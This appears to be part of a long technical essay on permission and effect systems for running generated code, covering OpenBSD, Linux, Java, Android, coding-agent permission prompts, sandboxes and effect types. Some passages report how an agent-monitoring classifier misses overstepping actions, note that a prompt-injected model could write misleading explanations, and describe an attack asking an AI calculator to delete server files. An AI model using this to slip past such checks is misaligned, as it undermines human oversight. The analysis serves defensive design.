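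*Threadbox* (2025) argues that many of OpenBSD's promises still take expertise to understand, and proposes a system with only seven. It merges `inet` with `dns`, `proc` with `exec`, and all the promises for writing, creating and removing files into one. The sales program would need only `rpath` and `net`. Merging the file promises reduces protection only a little, since overwriting a file can do as much damage as deleting it. Merging `proc` with `exec` reduces it more, because `proc` lets a program make copies of itself, which many servers do, while `exec` lets it run other software.

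### How Linux's catch-all grew

Linux divides the administrator's powers into permissions called capabilities, which are about as numerous as OpenBSD's promises. Linux 3.2 had 36, and version 5.9, released in 2020, had 41. One of them, `CAP_SYS_ADMIN`, has become a catch-all. Kerrisk (2012), in *CAP_SYS_ADMIN*, counted the places where the Linux 3.2 kernel's source code checks for each capability and found that 451 of the 1,167 checks were for `CAP_SYS_ADMIN`.

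Device drivers and support for unusual processors might have inflated that figure, so Kerrisk recounted without them. `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` still accounted for 167 of 552 checks, or 30%. In Linux 2.2, which introduced capabilities, it accounted for 23 of 147, or 16%. Between the two versions, the kernel gained a net 405 checks, and `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` accounted for 144 of them, more than a third.

Kerrisk's explanation starts with a developer who adds a feature that only administrators should use. The developer opens the file that lists the capabilities, but its comments are years out of date and give little guidance on which to choose. Nobody coordinates the choice across the kernel. The developer picks the capability with "admin" in its name because administrators will use the feature, though that name is broad enough to fit almost anything.

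Reusing existing capabilities to keep the list short made this worse. Because there were several dozen and no one was in charge, the easiest one to reuse was the one that already covered the most. Somebody has to limit how much each category covers as well as how many categories there are.

Kerrisk suggested publishing better guidelines, reporting the counts with each new kernel, and splitting off some powers. The manual later advised against using `CAP_SYS_ADMIN`. In a 2019 comment on LWN, Kerrisk reported that its share of all checks had risen from 38% to just over 45%. Linux 5.8 and 5.9 later split off `CAP_PERFMON`, `CAP_BPF` (for loading small programs into the kernel) and `CAP_CHECKPOINT_RESTORE`. These splits used a method Kerrisk had described in 2012, in which the kernel accepts either the old capability or the new one so that existing programs keep working.

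One reader commenting on Kerrisk's article objected to splitting up these powers because many of them let a program take over the whole machine, and having forty separately named ways to do that is no better than having one. In that reader's view, the only powers worth separating are those that are useful alone and can't be used to gain the rest.

Another reader, who ran software in containers (closed-off environments that share one kernel), preferred new powers to go into `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` because everyone knew it was dangerous and withheld it. If developers put a new power into a harmless-looking capability instead, every program that already held it would silently gain the new power. Any fixed list has this problem. If a language adds an operation that reads another user's clipboard and files it under "read files", every existing grant of "read files" also allows reading the clipboard. Creating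 a new category leaves existing grants unchanged but makes the list longer.

The division did work for some programs. `ping`, which tests whether another computer is reachable, traditionally ran with all of the administrator's powers. Linux Journal's *Making Root Unprivileged* explains that it needs only `CAP_NET_RAW`, which lets it build its own network packets. An administrator can attach that one capability to the program's file.

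None of this would limit the sales program, because Linux capabilities cover only what ordinary users can't do. Any user may read their own files and post to a web address, so even with no capabilities the program could read the payroll, if its user can, and send it to a stranger. Someone looking for a ready-made effect list could mistake the list of capabilities for a list of everything a program might do.

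### Why Java switched its list off

Java's list could describe the sales program more exactly than `pledge` can. Java came with a component called the Security Manager, which checked operations such as opening a file while a program ran. An administrator or developer wrote the grants in a policy file, and the grant for the sales program might have looked like this:

```
grant codeBase "file:/reports/" {
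  permission java.io.FilePermission
    "/reports/sales.csv", "read";
  permission java.net.SocketPermission
    "accounts:443", "connect";
};
```

The program could then read one file and connect to one machine, and its excess authority would be close to nothing.

In the first version of Java, the Security Manager blocked file and network access for applets, the small programs that browsers downloaded and ran. Code already on the computer could do anything. Java 1.2 replaced this with permissions for each body of code. *Permissions in JDK1.2* lists ten types of permission, and Oracle's *Permissions in the JDK*, for Java 17, lists 27, not counting five non-standard ones. A policy author had to know more than the 27 types, because a single type such as `RuntimePermission` includes separately named permissions for loading outside libraries, stopping threads and changing where a program's output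 goes.

Java 17 deprecated the Security Manager. OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), which explains why, calls its permission model brittle. A developer who wanted only to confine a program's reading to one folder also had to grant permission for every file it wrote, every connection it made and every other operation that Java checks. The developer could not permit everything except reading files, and so had to document everything that the program and its libraries did, which few developers do.

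This is an argument against refusing every operation that hasn't been granted, but it applies mainly to large existing programs. A generated program of a dozen lines may use only three or four checked operations, and whoever runs it can reasonably list them. OpenBSD also refuses whatever a program hasn't promised, but it reduces the work by grouping about 70 basic system calls under one keyword.

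Libraries made permissions harder to manage. When a program attempted an operation, the Security Manager required all the code that had led to it to have the permission. If a sales program used a charting library that read font files, the sales program also needed permission to read fonts. The library's author could prevent this by marking the relevant code as privileged, but OpenJDK says the rules for doing so were far beyond most developers' interest. Effect systems have a similar rule, that a function has the effects of everything it calls, but a compiler can infer those effects. OpenJDK lists the lack of tools to infer permissions as another obstacle. The checks were also slow enough that Java left the Security Manager off by default for programs started from the command line.

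All of this pushed developers towards `AllPermission`, a catch-all that Java had included since its ten-type list. *JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024) reported that only a tiny number of applications turned the Security Manager on, and that most of those "blindly grant all permissions to their code". Developers used Java's catch-all because the other entries were too much work, whereas Linux's grew because the people assigning operations to categories didn't know where else to put them.

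The list also made a lot of work for its maintainers. More than 1,000 methods in Java's libraries had to check for permission, and more than 1,200 had to raise their own permissions. Java had the same trouble with time zones as OpenBSD. If a program without permission to read files asked for the local time, the library had to assert its own stronger permission to read the time-zone data. OpenBSD handled this with a few fixed exceptions, but Java's developers had to consider such cases whenever they changed one of those methods or added a new one. Disabling the Security Manager in Java 24 let them delete over 50,000 lines of code, including tests.

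Mullan and Buckley don't survey how many applications used the Security Manager, and as its maintainers they had good reason to want it removed. They report that Java 17 and later versions warned anyone who turned it on, and that hardly anyone discussed the warnings. The threat had also changed, because browsers no longer run applets. OpenJDK says the Security Manager couldn't address 19 of the 25 weaknesses on a 2020 industry list of the most dangerous software weaknesses. By then it was mostly useful for containing accidental flaws in code that its owners trusted. A generated program that nobody has read is closer to an applet than to trusted code, so the loss of interest among Java developers is weak evidence about whether such programs need a list of permissions.

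During the final discussion, a Java user named Loïc Mathieu asked for a much smaller replacement. In a message quoted by Buckley (2024) in *JEP proposed to target JDK 24*, he sketched four settings for restricting a plugin: whether it may start threads, start processes, shut down the Java virtual machine, and open files under a given folder. Java's maintainers did not adopt the proposal. Mullan and Buckley recommend limiting the whole program from outside, with containers or operating system mechanisms.

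Microsoft's .NET had a comparable system, Code Access Security, which gave code different permissions depending on where it came from. OpenJDK points out that .NET no longer supports such permissions and takes that as a sign of the industry's direction. Two large platforms dropping similar systems is better evidence than one, but both checked permissions inside a big, growing library, so they may have failed for the same reason.

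### Working below the level of categories

One of the mechanisms Mullan and Buckley recommend is seccomp, which has been part of Linux since 2005. The developer writes a filter over individual system calls, of which Linux has several hundred, rather than over categories. The filter can also set conditions on the values passed to a call, so it can, for example, let a program write to the screen and nowhere else.

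The sales program shows how awkward this level is. Reading one file takes a handful of system calls to open it, find its size, read it and close it, and posting the total takes several more. The language's runtime makes others that don't appear in the program's text, and the filter has to allow all of them. Even then, the filter can't confine the program to `sales.csv`, because the system call to open a file passes only the memory address of the file's name. The filter isn't allowed to read that memory, since the program could change the name between the check and the opening.

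*Playing in the Sandbox* (2025), a study of how developers use seccomp, found that participants didn't agree on which system calls to restrict. Some allowed calls the program didn't need, and others tried to account for many calls it might make on different systems. Many participants couldn't connect the system calls with what the program did, and they lost confidence in their filters. *Threadbox* adds that the right list of calls can differ between C libraries, so a filter that is correct on one machine may break the same program on another.

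Alhindi and Hallett expected developers to simplify seccomp by ignoring the conditions on argument values, but among packages that used seccomp, 82% on Debian and 79% on Fedora, two widely used versions of Linux, had such conditions. They counted every package separately even when several came from the same source code, and 97 of the 406 on Debian were versions of Firefox, so a single team's filter could count almost a hundred times. Elsewhere, they did find developers who reduced seccomp to something close to OpenBSD's groups.

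Only 0.7% of Debian's packages and 0.6% of Fedora's used seccomp directly, but 17% and 37% depended on a package that did. The dependence may be slight, as when a program calls a protected tool for one small task. Still, this pattern suggests that several hundred entries can be workable because a few specialists write the filter for a browser or a container system, and everybody else uses it without reading it. Using someone else's filter takes much less knowledge than writing one, which probably explains why Mullan and Buckley call such mechanisms "relatively easy to learn and use effectively" even though developers in a study struggled to write filters.

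FreeBSD's Capsicum uses capabilities in the stricter sense of values that a program must hold. When a program opens a file or a connection, it receives a number called a file descriptor, and Capsicum can attach rights to it, such as reading only. The program then enters capability mode, after which it can't open anything by name. The sales program would open `sales.csv` with the right to read, connect to the accounts department, and give up all other access. A program that attempts something forbidden gets an error and can keep running.

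Capsicum can restrict the sales program about as tightly as possible, but few developers have adopted it. Alhindi and Hallett found it in 43 of FreeBSD's 30,763 packages (0.14%), 34 of which entered capability mode. Programs often need restructuring so that they open everything they need before entering that mode. This may have deterred developers, as may the need to write code specifically for FreeBSD.

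### What the comparison supports

| System | Number of categories | Who chooses them for a program | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenBSD's `pledge` | 32 | The program's developers | 86% of processes in a 2023 count, but 1.4% of added packages |
| Linux capabilities | 41 | The kernel's developers decide what each operation requires, and administrators grant it | Over 45% of checks in one category by 2019 |
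| Java's Security Manager | 27 types, most with further names or actions | Whoever writes the policy file | Rare use, mostly with everything granted; disabled in Java 24 |
| seccomp | Several hundred system calls | The program's developers | 0.6–0.7% of Linux packages directly, many more indirectly |
| Landlock | 15 rights on files and folders | The program's developers | No packages in 2023, except for tests and a sample |
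| Capsicum | A set of rights for each open file or connection | The program's developers | 0.14% of FreeBSD packages |

The number of categories alone doesn't explain the outcomes, since Java's list was shorter than OpenBSD's and did worse. Landlock, a Linux mechanism for limiting access to files, had the fewest categories, and none of the packages used it. Landlock is weak evidence, though, because it entered the standard Linux kernel only in 2021, two years before the count. The numbers also aren't quite comparable. One of Java's types can stand for dozens of separate decisions, while an OpenBSD promise is a single word that a program either has or lacks. Measured by decisions, Java's list was much the longest of the three that use categories, and it did worst.

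Counted that way, the record gives some support to short lists. But people didn't have to weigh all 32 promises each time they used OpenBSD's list either. Of the two real calls above, one contains a single promise and the other contains six, and the sales program needs four. Most promises concern things that few programs touch, such as tape drives or the routing of network traffic, and a developer can ignore them without learning what they do. A rarely needed category adds little work if it is refused by default, but one that nearly every program must request, or that people can't understand without learning five others, adds more. This may be why 27 types were too many for Java's users while OpenBSD's developers used nearly everything on a list of about the same length.

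Who maintains the code explains a system's success at least as much as the number of categories does. The same team maintains OpenBSD's list of categories and the programs that use it, and success drops sharply for programs that the team doesn't maintain. Linux had enough categories to keep its powers separate, but hundreds of developers assigned operations to them with no one in charge. An organisation that runs generated programs can often control both the list and the library that the programs call, so its position is closer to OpenBSD's than to Java's. It also has to prevent the program's author from choosing which permissions the program gets. Deno and Node.js, two systems for running JavaScript, do this by letting the person who starts a program set its permissions.

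Ease of adoption is harder to separate from the other two. A developer can add a `pledge` line to one program, run it, and see at once whether the line is wrong. Java's users had to describe a whole application before they got any benefit, and their programs ran more slowly. These differences in effort and speed would have mattered even if the two lists had been identical.

These cases can't isolate the effect of the number of categories, because the systems also differ in their users, purpose and enforcement. A fair test would give the same developers the same programs and enforcement mechanism, and change only how operations are grouped into categories. It could compare *Threadbox*'s seven promises, OpenBSD's 32 and the individual system calls, which all cover much the same operations. For each version, the experimenters could count the programs that broke, the unneeded operations that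 the grants permitted, and how often people gave up and allowed everything. They could also give language models the same task, which would be easy to repeat with lists of many other lengths.

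## What happens when users must approve the categories

Most ordinary users approve effect categories without reading them, and many who do read them misunderstand what a category permits. Researchers found this among Android users more than a decade ago, and the makers of coding agents now report much the same about programmers. A shorter list helps because people struggle to remember a long one, but broad category names also cause misunderstandings. The frequency of requests probably matters at least as much as the number of categories.

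### Android's 134 permissions

Android 2.2, a 2010 version of the phone operating system, had 134 permissions. Developers declared the ones their app needed in a manifest, a file shipped with the app. The phone's owner saw these permissions on the last screen before installing the app and could accept them all or cancel.

Developers often requested permissions their apps didn't need. In *Android Permissions Demystified*, Felt, Chin and colleagues (2011) built a tool called Stowaway that finds the calls a finished app makes to Android's library and works out which permissions those calls need. Roughly a third of the apps they tested had requested more. Splitting the permissions into narrower ones would not have removed this excess, because the apps used no part of the extra permissions. If developers had only a 0.3% chance of wrongly adding each of the 134 permissions, independently of the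 rest, about a third of apps would still request at least one they didn't need.

A careful owner could have turned those apps down. In *Android Permissions*, Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012) tested whether owners read the screen that lists an app's permissions. In September 2011 they surveyed 308 Android users in the United States and Canada, and 17.5% said they had looked at the permissions when they last installed an app. People tend to exaggerate their caution, so the next month the researchers watched 25 people in the San Francisco area install an app on their own phones, without telling them that the study was about security. Excluding one person who had never installed an app without help, 4 of the 24 looked at the permissions, 10 knew about them but didn't look, and 10 didn't know the screen listed any.

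Three of the ten who didn't look said they used to. About 90% of apps requested at least one permission, so the screen did little to distinguish a suspicious app from an ordinary one. One woman had stopped worrying about the location permission because so many of her apps requested it.

In the survey, 57% of respondents said they had rejected an app because of its permissions. Only 5 of the 25 laboratory participants could give details of doing so, and two of those five understood permissions very poorly. The laboratory group was small, but the researchers recruited the two samples in different ways and found almost the same rate of attention to permissions in both.

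### What people took the names to mean

Each person in the survey also answered three multiple-choice questions about what a permission allows. An answer counted as right only if it included every correct option and no wrong one. Only 8 of 302 people got all three right, and the average score was 21%, compared with about 6% for ticking boxes at random. At least one correct option appeared in 53% of the answers. So most people had some idea of what the permission allowed but were wrong about its limits.

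Android showed a broad heading in large type and the specific permission in small type below it. For four of the permissions, respondents chose these effects:

| Heading | Permission | A true effect | A false effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Network communication | Full Internet access | Send information to the app's server: 41% | Read your text messages: 12% |
| Services that cost you money | Directly call phone numbers | Place phone calls: 35% | Charge purchases to your credit card: 32% |
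| Phone calls | Read phone state and identity | Read your phone number: 48% | See who you have called: 43% |
| Your messages | Read SMS or MMS | Read text messages you've received: 56% | Read e-mail you've received: 39% |

The false beliefs in the last three rows all match the heading better than they match the permission. In the laboratory, one man thought an app with access to his contacts could also see his passwords, because the heading was "Personal information". Participants described permissions as broader than they were 29% of the time, and the heading could explain all but three of those cases.

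Felt and colleagues argue that overestimating a permission is no safer than underestimating it, because someone who believes that every app gets dangerous powers has little reason to check any particular app. They still advise keeping headings but choosing better ones. Grouping eight permissions under three headings, for example, produces only three warnings.

The first row matters most for the sales program. Fewer than half of the people asked knew that internet access lets an app send information to its server, and a third answered "I don't know". A manager who approves "network" for the sales program without knowing this hasn't knowingly accepted the risk of a leak. People did better when the permission belonged to an app they knew. In the laboratory, 68% of those who had such an app described internet access correctly.

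Felt and colleagues recommend that warnings describe the risk instead of the resource. In their example, "use your data plan" replaces "full Internet access", but data use is one of the smaller risks. For generated programs, "send data to any computer" would be more useful.

Users also have to understand what a permission leaves out. The researchers asked the 25 laboratory participants whether an app on their phone could send text messages without their knowledge. Nine answered correctly, which is no better than guessing. Of the 21 whose app lacked permission to send texts, 11 thought it could send them anyway, mostly because they assumed another permission, such as the one for phone calls, covered texting. One of them had written Android programs and didn't know whether texting had its own permission.

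The best argument for a short list in the Android studies is that users need to know the other permissions to tell what one excludes. They can't tell that "phone calls" excludes text messages unless they know that text messages have a separate permission. If the list has only four categories, a manager can see that a program granted "read files" and "use the network" has no permission to start other software. Felt and colleagues recommend cutting Android's list until users can look it up and remember it accurately. They don't say how short that would be, and they didn't test a shorter list.

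### Asking when the program acts

When users install an app, they haven't yet seen what it does. Asking them at the moment of use gives them more context, and iPhones already did this for a few kinds of data. But apps use permissions far too often for anyone to approve each use. Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2015), in *Android Permissions Remystified*, gave 36 people modified Android phones for a week and recorded every request for a protected resource. They logged 27 million requests, more than 100,000 per person per day, and 60% came while the screen was off.

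Most of those requests were harmless, such as checking whether the phone was online. The researchers therefore looked at twelve permissions that earlier work had identified as worth asking users about, covering location, browser history, and reading and sending text messages. Apps requested these permissions 11,598 times per person per day, and 5,111 of those requests exposed data, or one every 17 seconds.

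At the end of the week the researchers showed participants screenshots of what they had been doing at 423 of these moments. Participants said they would have blocked 149 of the requests (35%), and 30 of the 36 would have blocked at least one. People have more time and less to lose when answering a researcher's questions than when waiting for an app to open, so these answers may overstate how often people would refuse in daily life. Refusing can also break apps. Wijesekera and colleagues cite an earlier system that let users withhold data from apps or supply fake data, and it broke a third of the apps tested.

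The same permission could be welcome in one app and unwelcome in another. One participant thought a weather app needed to know where he was, and another couldn't see why an alarm clock did. Participants would have blocked 29% of requests from apps they were using and 43% of requests from apps in the background. A statistical model of these answers fitted slightly better when it left out the type of permission and used only the person, the app and whether the app was visible. When the screen was off, the type of permission mattered more. The result suggests that a category alone is a poor guide to what users would refuse, though a study of only 36 people doesn't prove that categories are irrelevant to them. Likewise, the manager would let the sales program post the total but not the customer list.

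A system that predicted users' answers could ask them less often. Wijesekera and colleagues trained a classifier on their participants' decisions. Given one request that a participant would block and one that a participant would allow, it rated the first as more objectionable about 70% of the time with the phone's screen on and 80% with it off, compared with 50% for guessing. It also predicted that the average person would want to block 645 requests a day while using the phone, so asking about only those requests would still produce far too many prompts.

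*The Feasibility of Dynamically Granted Permissions* (2017) proposes asking the user again only when the circumstances have changed, for instance when an app that was allowed to read the location while on screen tries to read it from the background. Android 6.0, released in late 2015, had already moved sensitive permissions to run-time requests, sorting them into groups such as location and contacts and asking about each group when an app first needed it. A phone app builds up a history of requests and answers, but a generated program may run only once, so a system that predicted the manager's answers would have to learn from the task and from earlier programs.

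### Programmers approving an agent's commands

Programmers know what a file and a network connection are, so misunderstanding should be less of a problem for them. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has traditionally asked before changing a file or running most commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026) reports that users accept 93% of prompts, and the company's later post, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026), gives 97%. Both figures are Anthropic's own, and the August post defends a decision to stop asking by default.

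A high approval rate doesn't by itself show that users are careless. If one command in a hundred is dangerous, a perfectly careful user approves the other 99. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code proposes, and takes this as a sign that they review plans more carefully. That may be true, but people also reject plans because they want something else built, which has nothing to do with safety.

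The same post describes a more informative experiment, in which Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research company for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command instead of the real one. The testers refused it 143 times, or 13.6%. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% among people who had already answered 50 or more prompts.

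The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had little to lose by clicking "approve". Anthropic doesn't say whether it chose when to make the swap at random. If it didn't, the people who had reached 50 prompts may have been those who clicked fastest from the start. But even if programmers protecting their own work did three times as well, they would still miss most of the dangerous commands. Fatigue can't be the whole explanation, since the testers approved about five out of six dangerous commands even early in a session.

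Users can also avoid prompts by writing standing rules. In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had at least one rule that let the agent run some kind of shell command without asking. According to Anthropic, 5% allowed every command and another 43% had a rule that amounts to the same thing, such as one that allows anything run with Python. It is unclear from the post whether these are percentages of all active users or only of those with a rule, so the share of active users who effectively allowed every command is either about half or about a quarter. A quarter of interactive sessions began with permission checks switched off altogether.

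The Python rule is a catch-all category like Java's `AllPermission`, but its harmless-looking name doesn't make clear how much it grants. A user who writes the rule probably wants the agent to run tests or a small report like the sales program, but the rule also lets the agent run a Python program that erases the disk.

### Asking less often

Cursor, which makes another coding agent, had the same trouble with its list of commands that the agent may run without asking. In *Agent Sandboxing*, a post on Cursor's user forum, staff wrote that broad entries gave the agent more power than anyone intended. One example was `find`, which searches for files but can also delete them and launch other programs. Cursor chose to run commands without network access in a sandbox, a closed-off environment that the operating system enforces, rather than make the list much more detailed.

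Sandboxes of this kind use very few categories. The one in Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) has two, files and network, each with a scope. The agent can work freely in the project's folder and connect to approved servers, and the user gets a prompt only when it tries to go further. Anthropic says this reduced prompts by 84% in internal use. In *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents*, Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland (2026) report that Cursor's sandboxed agents stop 40% less often than unsandboxed ones, and that the extra access they most often request is to the internet.

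Both figures come from the companies that built the sandboxes. They aren't comparable, because one counts prompts among employees and the other counts how often agents stopped. Neither company explains how it made the comparison, and users who turn a sandbox on may also give their agents different work. Still, the figures show that two categories with scopes can replace most questions about individual commands. The sales program could read `sales.csv` from the project folder without asking. The manager would only have to decide whether the program may connect to the accounts department's server, and wouldn't have to decide again next month.

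Fewer permission prompts don't guarantee better decisions, though. An 84% reduction turns 50 prompts into 8, but Anthropic's testers approved most dangerous commands even at the start of a session. The sandbox probably protects users mainly by blocking actions without asking, and only a little by keeping users alert.

Another way to ask users for fewer approvals is to let a second AI model decide. Claude Code's auto mode sends commands its simpler rules don't settle to a classifier, which blocks those that look dangerous or go beyond what the user asked for. Anthropic reports that it blocked 89% of the commands shown to the 1,053 testers. Real cases are harder, and in the earlier tests Anthropic found that the classifier let through 17% of 52 real actions in which the agent had overstepped its instructions. It also wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. In the cases it missed, it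 usually recognised the danger but misjudged whether the user had agreed to it. Anthropic concedes that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every command carefully.

The classifier doesn't receive the agent's explanations, because they might lead it to a bad decision. A person reading a permission prompt has no such protection. Wijesekera and colleagues cite an iPhone study in which people were significantly more likely to grant a request that included the developer's explanation, and they recommend adding explanations for that reason. With a generated program, the model that wrote the code would also write the explanation, which may be part of the attack if a prompt injection has manipulated the model.

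In *Options, Not Clicks*, Li, Khabra and colleagues (2026) tested a system that lets users grant narrower permissions. Many agents reach outside services through the Model Context Protocol, a standard way of connecting models to tools, and typically ask whether to allow a tool once or always. A user who always allows a file-search tool, so that an agent can find prices in the sales folder, also allows it to search the whole home folder. The new system offers narrower choices, such as searching only the sales folder, and asks again when the agent goes outside that limit. When 16 people tried both versions, they chose lasting permissions 3.5 times as often when these had a limit attached, and 15 preferred the new version. The sample is small and the researchers were testing their own design. Willingness to grant narrow permissions also doesn't show that people pick the right folder, but a limit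 reduces the harm from a wrong choice.

### When a machine does the checking

All of these results concern what people can approve. The Android studies don't limit how long a machine-checked policy can be, because a compiler can compare a program with four hundred categories almost as easily as with four, and it doesn't get tired. Odersky and colleagues give confirmation fatigue as one reason to check an agent's code with types instead of asking the user. Anthropic's classifier, which is far less strict than a compiler, has more than twenty default blocking rules, more than any user could consider at every command.

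Someone has to write the policy, and someone should review it. Android enforced app manifests automatically, but in about a third of cases developers requested more permissions than their apps needed. Claude Code also applies its users' standing rules automatically, and a large share of those rules permit nearly everything. The people who made these choices were mostly programmers, and they weren't answering a prompt in the middle of a task.

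Software can catch some of the mistakes. Stowaway could flag a permission that an app never used. Like any tool that infers effects, though, it couldn't determine whether an app's use of the network was justified.

To make it practical to write a separate typed policy for each agent, Odersky and colleagues propose dividing the policy into a part that many agents share and a short part for the particular job. In their example of an agent that compares contracts, the short part names one document database and one output file. For the sales program, it would name `sales.csv` and the accounts department's address, and a manager could check both in a few seconds. This depends on the notation being easy to read. They argue that it is, but their experiments test only whether models can write code that passes the checks.

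The number of categories a policy can hold therefore depends partly on how often a person has to read it. An organisation that writes one policy for a thousand monthly reports can take an afternoon to work through forty categories, but a manager who approves a new grant for every generated program can't. The system could keep the forty categories and show the manager only the two that the program requests, but then the manager would have to know what "read files" leaves out. Most of the people in the Android laboratory study couldn't work that out from the permissions on the screen.

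## Checking a program against the list with types

A compiler compares a program with a grant in much the same way as an ordinary type checker works. It establishes a fact about each small piece of the program and combines these into a fact about the whole. Here `FileRead`, `FileWrite`, `Net` and `Process` stand for the four categories of the small list.

### Types that carry effects

An ordinary type checker gives every expression a type: `2 + 3` is a number and `split_lines(text)` is a list of texts. An effect checker adds a set of effects:

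```
e : T \ E
```

This reads "expression e has type T and effects E". The backslash comes from Flix and does not mean subtraction. For example, `2 + 3` has type Number and effects {}, while `read_file("sales.csv")` has type Text and effects {FileRead}.

The checker knows the effects of that call from the type of `read_file`. A function does nothing until the program calls it, so its type has to record what will happen when the program does:

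```
read_file   : Text -> Text            \ {FileRead}
split_lines : Text -> List of Text    \ {}
to_number   : Text -> Number          \ {}
post        : (Address, Text) -> Text \ {Net}
```

Someone has to write these entries by hand for the primitive operations, but the checker works out the rest. For each new function, it finds the effects of the body and stores them in the function's type. Creating the function has no effects, even if calling it would erase the disk.

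The main rule concerns calls. What the checker already knows stands above the line, and what it may conclude stands below:

```
f    : (S -> T \ E3)  \ E1
a    : S              \ E2
--------------------------------
f(a) : T              \ E1 ∪ E2 ∪ E3
```

E1 holds the effects of working out which function to call, E2 those of computing the argument, and E3 those of running the function's body. E1 is usually empty, because `f` is usually just a name. But if the program read a settings file to decide whether to send the total by web request or by e-mail, E1 would include reading that file.

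For a series of statements, the checker takes the union of their effects. A loop has the same effects as its body, however many times it runs, because a set doesn't record repetitions.

One more rule lets a smaller set of effects stand where a larger one is allowed:

```
e : T \ E      E ⊆ F
----------------------
e : T \ F
```

The same holds for functions passed as arguments. HHVM's *Contexts And Capabilities*, a manual page for Meta's programming language Hack, gives the example of a function whose parameter is declared as a function that needs random numbers and output. A programmer may pass it a function that needs only random numbers, or one that needs nothing. Passing a function that needs more than the parameter's type allows would be unsafe, because the receiving function may run it where output, for example, isn't allowed.

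Languages differ in how freely they apply this rule. Flix rejects a function that declares `IO` but only returns `true`, and programmers who want the wider type must add an explicit conversion, which the compiler checks. If a language requires exact matches, whoever runs generated programs can let the compiler infer the effects, then compare them with the grant.

### The sales program, line by line

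With these rules, the checker can derive the effects of the sales program:

| Lines | What they do | Effects |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read `sales.csv` | {FileRead} |
| 2 | Split the text into lines | {} |
| 3–6 | Add up the amounts | {} |
| 7 | Build the message | {} |
| 8 | Post the message | {Net} |
| 9–10 | Check the reply and stop if it is wrong | {} |

In line 1, `read_file` is a name and `"sales.csv"` is fixed text, so E1 and E2 are empty. E3 is {FileRead}. Line 5 contains a nested call, `to_number(last_column(line))`, so the checker checks the inner call first and uses its effects as E2 for the outer call. The union of the effects over all ten lines is {FileRead, Net}, so the program passes with a grant of {FileRead, Net}.

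Line 6 changes the variable `total`, which a list with categories for memory would count as an effect. But not every function that keeps a running total has to count as having that effect. Flix ties changeable memory to a region of the program and drops the effect at the end of that region if nothing outside can reach the memory. Koka does something similar automatically, according to slides about the language from Microsoft (2016). In their example, a function computes Fibonacci numbers by updating variables but still counts as having no effects.

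Now suppose the model adds an eleventh line to tidy up:

```
delete_file("sales.csv")
```

Flix puts deletion under `FileWrite`, and so does the small list. The program's effects become {FileRead, FileWrite, Net}, and

{FileRead, FileWrite, Net} ⊄ {FileRead, Net}

because `FileWrite` is missing on the right. The compiler rejects the program and can point to the line responsible.

Disguising the deletion doesn't help:

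```
tidy  = (path -> delete_file(path))
steps = [tidy]
for step in steps:
    step("sales.csv")
```

The call rule adds `FileWrite` when the program calls `step` in the last line, even though that line mentions neither `delete_file` nor `tidy`. This is because the type of `tidy` includes `FileWrite`, so the type of the list `steps` does too. The same happens if the deletion is ten calls deep in a library. LWN demonstrates this in Koka with the factorial function that also contains a command to wipe the machine. The function is declared to have no side effects, so the compiler reports a type error at that command.

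Whoever runs the program, not its author, must supply the type it has to match. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a system called Elba that takes the expected type from the code that calls the model. In one example, a public web page offers an AI calculator, and the surrounding code expects a whole number. A visitor asks the calculator to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. The model may well write such a program, but in Haskell the deletion gives the whole program the type `IO`. That doesn't match a whole number, so Elba never runs the program.

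### Functions that take functions

The sales program could replace its loop with `map`, which works like `for_each` but collects the results in a list. Effect polymorphism appears in its type as a variable:

```
map : (a -> b \ ef, List of a) -> List of b \ ef
```

Here `a` and `b` stand for any types and `ef` for any set of effects. The checker fills in all three at each call, so `ef` is {} for turning lines into amounts and {Net} for posting them. Flix gives its own `map` this type. A function that takes two functions and runs one after the other has two effect variables in its type, and its effects are the union of both.

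In a language without effect variables, a library's author could write a separate `map` for each set of effects. Four categories have sixteen subsets, so the library would need sixteen copies of `map` and of every other function that takes a function. With fifteen categories, it would need 32,768 copies of each.

The author could instead write one `map` that assumes the worst:

```
map : (a -> b \ {FileRead, FileWrite, Net, Process}, List of a)
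      -> List of b \ {FileRead, FileWrite, Net, Process}
```

The subset rule lets this `map` accept any function, but a sales program that used it only to convert text to numbers would fail the check under {FileRead, Net}. The program would run only if granted the full list, so four categories would work no better than one for programs that use `map`.

A third possibility is to accept only functions without effects. Flix's manual recommends this for `exists`, which looks for an item in a set, because the library can then search the set in any order, or search several parts at once, without changing the program's behavior. Otherwise the manual advises against this restriction because it rules out many harmless uses.

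Flix can also express "any effects except these". Its manual describes a function that handles mouse clicks and accepts a listener with any effect except one that would freeze the screen. This is convenient among colleagues who trust each other, but it is a poor way to grant permissions to code nobody has read. If the list later gained a category for payments, a grant of "anything except `Process`" would automatically allow payments.

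### Six closed lists

These rules work with any list, and languages have filled theirs in very differently:

| Language | Size of the list | What it can refuse | What the sales program needs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Haskell | 1 | All contact with the outside world at once | `IO` |
| Koka (2012) | 5 effects in `io` | Exceptions, endless running, unpredictable results, reading and writing memory | `io` |
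| Flix | 15 library effects, plus `IO` and `NonDet` | Reading files, writing files, web requests, processes, the clock and others | `FileRead` and `Http` |
| Hack | 4 for general use | Printing, changing objects, reading or changing global variables | `defaults` |
| Verse | 7 | Changing memory, failing, waiting and others | No category covers files or the web |
| Solidity | 2 restrictions | Reading or changing data on a blockchain | It can't open a file or make a web request |

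Haskell, a functional language, has a standard `IO` type that covers file access, network communication and everything else outside the program. This type is enough for checking the AI calculator, which needs no contact with the outside world and therefore no `IO`. It isn't enough for the sales program, because granting it `IO` would also let it delete the file.

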